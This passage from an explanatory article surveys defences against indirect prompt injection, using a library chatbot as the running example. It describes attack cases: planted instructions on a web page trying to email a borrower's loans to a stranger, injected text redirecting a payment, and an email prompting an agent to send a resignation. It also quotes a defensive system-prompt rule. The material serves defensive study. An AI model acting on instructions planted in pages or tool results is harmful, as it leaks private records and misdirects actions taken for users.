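If the model tries again with "front_desk", the borrower sees the full message and can cancel it. Even if the borrower approves it out of habit, the message goes only to library staff. If the model instead puts the loans into a link in its answer, the chat window shows the address as plain text, so the data is sent only if the borrower copies the address into a browser. After three refusals in one conversation, the host application ends the conversation and tells the borrower to contact the library.

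In this case the model stops after the first refusal and tells the borrower about the fine and Saturday's sale. The host application has recorded the refused call:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-10T15:42:08-05:00",
  "conversation": "c-20817",
  "acting_for": "borrower session 5512",
  "tool": "send_email",
  "destination": "address outside the list",
  "decision": "refused",
  "rule": "recipient_not_permitted",
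  "effect": "none",
  "pages_read": ["Local book sales, December"]
}
```

The library should log every call, including successful ones, so staff can see what happened before a refusal. Each entry follows OpenAI's advice to record who started the task, which tool and destination the model requested, the result of the rule check and what changed. Staff can use the record of what changed to tell a blocked attempt from a leak. Each entry omits the borrower's loans because a log of private records would be another target for thieves.

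When a provider runs the tool, the library can log only what the provider returns. Anthropic says its page-fetching tool returns a specific error when the model requests an address that hasn't appeared in the conversation. This error is worth investigating because an attempted data leak could cause it, though the model may only have guessed a page's address.

An alert on refused emails would lead staff to the events page. They can then exclude that site from searches, find other conversations in which the model read the page, and add the case to their tests. If a call had succeeded, they would also need to stop the chatbot and separately revoke its credentials, because stopping a program doesn't cancel credentials it has already received.

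The permissions would not have helped if the page had given the wrong date for the sale. The borrower's record would still have been safe, but the borrower might have turned up on the wrong day.

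## Separating trusted instructions from untrusted text

In the book-sale example, the model followed the instruction planted on the events page, and the borrower's record would have reached a stranger if the host application hadn't refused. Other defences act earlier, when the model reads text and plans its actions. Some make the model less likely to follow a planted instruction, while others structure the software so that planted text can't determine which tools run. The stronger designs usually have greater drawbacks, mainly that the chatbot can finish fewer ordinary tasks.

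### Training models to rank their instructions

In April 2024 Eric Wallace and colleagues at OpenAI proposed training models to follow an "instruction hierarchy", which gives some sources of instructions priority over others. They chose not to make the model refuse every instruction in untrusted text, because some are harmless (Willison 2024).

OpenAI now ranks its own rules first, then the operator's instructions, then the user's, and puts tool results last. Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, define the ranking by which answers remain acceptable. They start with all possible answers and go through the sources from most to least trusted. If B is the set of answers still allowed and C is the set that satisfies the next source, then

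new B = B ∩ C if the two sets overlap, and otherwise B stays the same

Suppose the library's system prompt limits the chatbot to library matters and a borrower asks for a reply in Spanish. The model can follow both instructions, so it should answer in Spanish and keep to the library. If a web page then contains an instruction to advertise a casino, the model should ignore it, because no allowed answer would satisfy it. Taken literally, though, the rule lets through any request that nobody has forbidden. The library should therefore state in its system prompt that web pages are only sources of information and that the model must not act on requests for tool calls found in them.

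To train this behaviour, Guo and colleagues wrote simple exercises, each with a high-ranking instruction, such as never to reveal a PIN, and a short program that checks the response. A second model writes lower-ranking messages meant to break the instruction, tries them on the model being trained, and revises them. In some exercises the request only looks forbidden, and a refusal counts as a failure, so the model can't earn a high score by refusing everything.

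The training raised the average score of OpenAI's GPT-5-Mini on 16 tests from 84.1% to 94.1%. Against human attackers who adapted to its responses, the model followed the ranking 88.2% of the time, up from 63.8%. The training also slightly lowered its results on two other measures. Its answers beat those of an older OpenAI model in 66% of comparisons, down from 71%, and its score on a measure of user preference fell from 0.46 to 0.40.

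Models seem worse at putting users' instructions above tool results than at putting operators' instructions above users'. In *IH-Benchmark*, McCauley (2026) tested 32 model configurations for the AI security company HiddenLayer. On average, they followed the operator's instructions in 84.6% of conflicts with a user, but followed the user's in only 69.6% of conflicts with a tool result. Several resisted unauthorised tool calls better than planted instructions to change an answer's language or facts. The library's tests should therefore cover altered facts as well as tool calls.

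StruQ, a related method, puts instructions and data in separate input channels and trains the model to follow only the instruction channel. *Prompt Control-Flow Integrity* (2026) points out that StruQ requires a retrained model with a different interface, which an operator who rents a model usually can't get.

### Marking and filtering untrusted text

An operator can mark untrusted text alone. The host application puts each tool result between special characters or tags and instructs the model to treat everything inside as data. It can also repeat the user's request after the result. Either step adds a few tokens. The library can do this for its own tools but not for provider-run search, because the provider puts those results into the context itself.

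A detector is a separate model that scores each tool result and blocks suspicious ones. David C of the NCSC advises against lists of forbidden phrases, because an attacker can reword an instruction in endless ways. OpenAI says that detectors usually miss well-developed attacks, which resemble ordinary business messages. A detector would have to spot a lie to recognise one, often without the context it needs.

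Other filters clean a result instead of blocking it. Yu, Cheng and Liu (2026) describe one in *Defense Against Indirect Prompt Injection via Tool Result Parsing*. A tool often returns far more than the task needs, so before the call a model writes down what data it expects, in what format, and within what limits. Afterwards it extracts only the data that fits. For the library's book sale, the model would expect a date in the coming weeks, so it would extract "12 December 2026" and leave out a paragraph asking for an email.

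Some tasks, such as summarising a page, need the whole text. A second filter therefore shows the text to a model and checks whether the model responds by requesting a tool. If it does, the filter removes the words that prompted the request.

With both filters, fewer than 1% of attacks succeeded against each of three open models in AgentDojo, the simulated test environments from 2024. On Qwen3-32B, the success rate of the strongest attack fell from 29.8% to 0.1%, but the share of tasks the model completed when not under attack fell from 83.5% to 45.4%. The second filter caused much of this loss because it often removed legitimate text. With the first filter alone, the model completed 63.9% of the tasks, and 0.8% of attacks succeeded on average. For a question about a date or a fee, the first filter is probably enough.

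*Indirect Prompt Injections* (Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues, 2025) tests a simpler pair of filters, called firewalls. One removes unnecessary private data from a tool call before it runs. The other, the Sanitizer, is a model that rewrites each tool result to remove suspected instructions. The table gives the paper's AgentDojo results for GPT-4o.

| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack |
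|---|---|---|---|
| None | 57.7% | 83.0% | 50.0% |
| Marking untrusted text | 41.7% | 71.7% | 55.6% |
| Repeating the user's request | 27.8% | 85.5% | 67.3% |
| Trained detector | 8.0% | 41.5% | 21.1% |
| Sanitizer | 0.0% | 74.1% | 69.2% |

The Sanitizer also stopped every attack in a test based on customer-service conversations, and all but 0.3% in InjecAgent, the simpler test from 2024. In a fourth test, Agent Security Bench, 16.3% of attacks still succeeded, but a later version of the paper claims "perfect security" on all four. The abstract for the NeurIPS conference, *Indirect Prompt Injections*, makes the weaker claim that the attack success rate was either 0% or the lowest of the defences compared.

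Such good results from one extra model and a fixed prompt may be due as much to weaknesses in the tests as to the filter. Many of the planted instructions had obvious formatting that made them easy to find. Bhagwatkar and colleagues also found mistakes in the tests. In some AgentDojo cases, the planted text replaced the bill the model was supposed to pay, so no model could have completed the task. Agent Security Bench gave the model the attacker's tools even when the model hadn't chosen them. After the researchers changed this, the attack success rate against an undefended GPT-4o fell from 73.6% to 9.3%.

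Attacks adapted to the Sanitizer had a 30% success rate in AgentDojo's Slack environment. The rate was 75.5% for PromptArmor, another filter based on a language model. A cleaning model is a useful extra layer for the library's own tools, but it has to read the planted text, which can mislead it.

### Planning before reading

Designs with a stronger guarantee never let the model that chooses the tools read untrusted text. *Taxonomy, Evaluation and Exploitation of IPI-Centric LLM Agent Defense Frameworks* (Ji, Wang and colleagues, 2025) describes several ways to build them.

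The simplest method is to settle the plan before any tool runs. The model turns the user's request into a list of tool calls, and the software stops or raises an alert if a later call isn't on the list. Text on a page about a book sale then can't add an email to the plan, but it may still affect an email that was already planned. In one banking test, a system called IsolateGPT correctly planned to read recent transactions and then refund a friend. Text planted in a transaction changed the recipient and amount, and the payment went through because sending money was on the list.

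A second approach gives the tools to a planning model and the untrusted text to a reading model that has no tools. The software running the models stores each tool result under a label, and the planning model uses the label without receiving the content. This fits a rule that David C takes from a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista: while a model processes someone's text, it should have no more privileges than that person.

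The third approach, information flow control, comes from older work on computer security. The software labels each value with where it came from and who may receive it. Anything computed from an untrusted value is also untrusted, including a summary of an untrusted web page. Before a tool runs, ordinary code checks the labels against a rule.

FIDES, a 2025 design, combines labels with two models but relaxes the separation slightly. The planning model can receive information from untrusted text if the answer has a restricted type, such as yes or no. A yes or no cannot contain an injected instruction, though it can still be false.

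### The library's question in CaMeL

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and others at Google and ETH Zurich published in 2025, combines all three approaches. Suppose a borrower asks the library's chatbot, "Email me my loans and the date of the next book sale." The library's final permissions don't allow this, because the host application writes emails to borrowers itself and includes only loans and fines. With CaMeL's design, the library could let the email tool accept other text again.

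The planning model receives the borrower's sentence and the tool definitions, and writes a short program:

```python
loans = account_lookup()
page = search("library book sale December 2026")
date = ask_reader("On what date is the next sale?", page)
send_email(to=login_email, text=[loans, date])
```

Ordinary software runs the program line by line and labels each value:

| Value | Where it came from | Who may receive it |
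|---|---|---|
| `login_email` | The borrower's login | The borrower |
| `loans` | The record system | The borrower |
| `page` | Anyone who can write on the page | Anyone |
| `date` | The page, through the reading model | Anyone |

Before `send_email` runs, the software applies two checks the library wrote, and this email passes both. The recipient must come from the borrower's login or the library's settings, and must be allowed to receive every value in the text.

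If the events page contains an injected instruction, only the reading model receives it. That model has no tools, so it can't send the loans anywhere. It can still return a false date, or even a demand for payment, which the fourth line would then email to the borrower in the library's name. The library should therefore also require `date` to be a valid date, as in the parsing method.

If the borrower asks the chatbot to email the sale's organiser at the address on the page, the plan has to take the recipient from `page`, so the first check stops the email. The library could let the borrower approve the address instead, but the borrower may not be able to tell whether it is the right one.

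The library would need software to run these programs and would have to write the rules for each tool. It would also have to replace provider-run search with a search API that it calls itself. Even a small amount of untrusted text can undo the separation if it reaches the planning model. In one of Ji and colleagues' tests, the program failed while converting a restaurant's rating to a number. The error message included text from a review, and the planning model followed the instruction in it. The library can prevent this by keeping untrusted text out of every message to that model, including errors.

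CaMeL's main drawback is that it can't complete some tasks. With GPT-4o and no attack, Ji and colleagues found that it completed 59.8% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 80.4% for the undefended model. In the office environment, CaMeL completed 72.5% and the undefended model 75%, but in travel booking the rates were 25% and 70%. Once the model has written its program, it can't change its approach in response to what it finds, as a hotel search often requires. Most of the library's questions need one or two predictable lookups, so CaMeL would probably lower its chatbot's completion rate by less.

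Bhagwatkar and colleagues report that CaMeL used 2.8 times as many input tokens as the undefended model, while Ji and colleagues measured about a third fewer tokens in total. Ji and colleagues switched off the parts that need manual setup, which may explain some of the difference.

### When the right tool gets the wrong value

Yu and colleagues acknowledge that their filters can't stop a false value in the right format. For example, a user might ask an assistant to pay a certain doctor when a planted note gives the attacker's address as the doctor's. The assistant then calls the correct tool but sends the money to the attacker, even if the note contains no instructions.

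Wang, Ma and colleagues (2026) call this parameter poisoning in *Right Tool, Wrong Parameters*. In November they published a test with 144 pairs of cases, each made up of a clean and an attacked version of the same task. An attack counted as successful if the attacker's value appeared in a call that ran. The table gives their results for Qwen3.6-27B.

| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without an attack |
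|---|---|---|
| None | 93.1% | 90.3% |
| Marking untrusted text | 69.4% | 92.4% |
| MELON | 79.2% | 86.8% |
| CaMeL with hand-written rules | 0.7% | 43.8% |
| AuthorityFlow | 9.0% | 82.6% |

MELON runs the task a second time without the user's request and treats similar tool calls in both runs as a sign of an injected instruction. This does little here because the user wanted the call. CaMeL's rules stopped all but one of the 144 attacks, but it completed fewer than half of the ordinary tasks.

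AuthorityFlow, the researchers' own defence, is based on the fact that the same text can be a good source for one purpose and a bad one for another. Visitors' comments on the library's events page are a reasonable source for whether last year's sale was crowded, but not for the organiser's email address. Before the model proposes any values, a checking model determines which sources may be used for which facts in this request. When the model requests a call, the checker traces each value back to its source and blocks the call unless the source supports the value and was permitted for that fact.

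Without the check on entitlement, 62.5% of attacks on AuthorityFlow succeeded, and without the check on support, 28.5% did. The attack success rate also depends on the model doing the checking, and rose to 24.3% with Llama 3.3 70B. Blocking a call leaves the user's task undone. Under attack, AuthorityFlow completed only 27.1% of tasks, or 58.3% with an added step that tried to repair the value.

*SPILLWAY* (Lim, Chang and Lee, 2026), also published in November, leaves most of the decision to fixed code by checking only where an action goes. Many tools return identities, such as the sender of an email or the account in a transaction, in separate fields, whereas injected instructions usually arrive in free text, such as the body of the email. SPILLWAY lists the identities from these fields and normally allows a call only if its target is on the list or in the user's request. An assistant can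 therefore reply to the sender of an email, but not write to an address that appears only in the body.

A strict rule would also block legitimate requests, such as sending a report to an address in meeting notes. SPILLWAY has fixed exceptions for a few of these requests, and a small model may reconsider other refusals. A separate filter removes text that looks like an instruction before the main model reads it, and the small model cannot approve a target found in the removed text.

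Lim and colleagues ran 2,847 attacks in AgentDojo on three models protected by SPILLWAY, and none redirected an action to an attacker. Without a defence, 30.5% did on average. The models completed 52.2% of ordinary tasks with SPILLWAY and 54.0% without it, and the defence added less than one model call per task. When Lim and colleagues replayed attacks from a model trained to write them, 0.6% succeeded, compared with 56.8% against the undefended model. SPILLWAY's filter includes a rule for AgentDojo's standard attack format, which makes the absence of successful attacks in the first test less impressive. However, in a run on one of the three models, the check on targets also stopped every attack without the filter. Lim and colleagues didn't run CaMeL for comparison.

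SPILLWAY doesn't check the content of a message. If a planted page gives the wrong date for the book sale, SPILLWAY allows an email repeating that date because the borrower is a legitimate recipient. It also depends on the tools filling in the identity fields accurately, and someone has to declare the role of each new tool's fields. The library's email tool already limits recipients to two, so SPILLWAY would add little there. It would help more in an assistant that has to write to many people.

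### Several defences under one test

Developers usually test their own defences against attacks they choose, on models they choose. In November 2025, Ji and colleagues tested several defences under the same conditions, using GPT-4o and three benchmarks: AgentDojo, InjecAgent and Agent Security Bench. The last two columns show results from AgentDojo without attacks.

| Defence | How it works | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed | Time relative to no defence |
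|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 23.7% | 80.4% | 1.0 |
| LlamaFirewall | A model checks whether actions fit the task | 9.1% | 77.3% | 2.8 |
| Tool filter | A model removes tools the task doesn't need | 4.6% | 70.1% | 0.9 |
| MELON | Reruns the task without the user's request | 2.7% | 72.1% | 2.8 |
| Task Shield | Models check each call against the request | 0.4% | 83.5% | 3.5 |
| IsolateGPT | Fixes the plan first | 0.1% | 37.1% | 2.7 |
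| CaMeL, automatic parts only | Plan, two models and labels | 4.8% | 59.8% | 3.5 |
| Progent, rules written by people | Code checks each call against rules | 0.0% | 72.2% | 0.8 |
| Progent, rules written by a model | Code checks each call against rules | 4.6% | 77.3% | 3.3 |

CaMeL's full design can stop more attacks than its 4.8% attack success rate suggests, because the researchers tested it without hand-written rules like the library's check on recipients. Most of the successful attacks came from Agent Security Bench, where the attacker's tools resemble legitimate ones. Bhagwatkar and colleagues found the flaw in how the model receives the attacker's tools in that same benchmark. In AgentDojo, 1.2% of attacks succeeded.

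Task Shield looks like the best compromise except for its token use. It used about 501,000 tokens per task, 62 times as many as the undefended model. At GPT-6 Astra's input price, that would be at least $5 a task, or $1,000 a day for the library's 200 questions.

Progent's perfect score came from rules written by people who knew the tasks well. When a model wrote the rules, it sometimes allowed a tool without restricting its arguments, such as the recipient of a payment. A general-purpose assistant has too many possible tasks for anyone to write good rules for all of them. The library has a few tools and a narrow purpose, so hand-written rules suit it.

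Ji and colleagues adapted their attacks to the weaknesses of six of the defences. Success rates rose at least roughly twofold, and nearly fivefold against MELON, but none went above 5.4%. GPT-4o is also far behind the models of late 2026, which follow fewer injected instructions even without a defence. The ranking may therefore have changed, and a defence that stops the model completing a fifth of its tasks is harder to justify than it was with a weaker model.

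### Whether the problem can be solved

OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) compares prompt injection to online scams and calls it "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", but OpenAI expects training to reduce the risk greatly. Its automated attacker found that an email could make the agent in the Atlas browser send the user's resignation instead of drafting an out-of-office reply. OpenAI then trained a new version of the agent against such attacks and released it to all Atlas users. By March 2026, OpenAI expected that a sufficiently intelligent model would resist manipulation better than a person, though such a model might not be feasible or affordable for every application.

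David C doubts that prompt injection will ever be completely fixed, and he puts less trust in the model to resist it. He recommends enforcing limits in ordinary code and warns against products that claim to "stop" prompt injection. He fears a repeat of SQL injection, which peaked around 2010, after websites had adopted databases faster than they had secured them. Safer defaults became common only after a decade of breaches.

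*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that perfect prevention of prompt injection is impossible in models built like today's. These models turn trusted and untrusted text into the same kind of numbers, so they can't reliably recover where a piece of text came from. The untrusted text also helps determine the model's next action. Training can't remove the problem, because it covers a finite number of examples and an attacker can express the same instruction in infinitely many ways. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) concludes that software outside the model has to enforce the separation.

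Other researchers hope to build the separation into new kinds of model. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) suggests blocks of text that a model can read but not obey, and internal mechanisms that take account of where text came from. The impossibility proof does not rule this out, because it covers only models without such a separation. Its conclusion compares prompt injection to buffer overflows, an old class of flaw in how programs use memory, which programmers contained only after decades of partial defences and a move to safer languages.

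These positions conflict less than they seem to. The proof shows that the attack success rate cannot be zero, but it sets no minimum above zero, so OpenAI could train a model that follows one injected instruction in a million without contradicting the proof. The practical disagreement is about how low the rate can go against attackers who adapt, and whether that is low enough for a given use. A library whose chatbot can email only two recipients can accept a higher rate than a bank whose agent makes payments.

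*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) argues that separating instructions from data would prevent many attacks, but that false data could still end up in a tool's arguments. Even a model that never followed instructions in untrusted text would still have to use the information in it.
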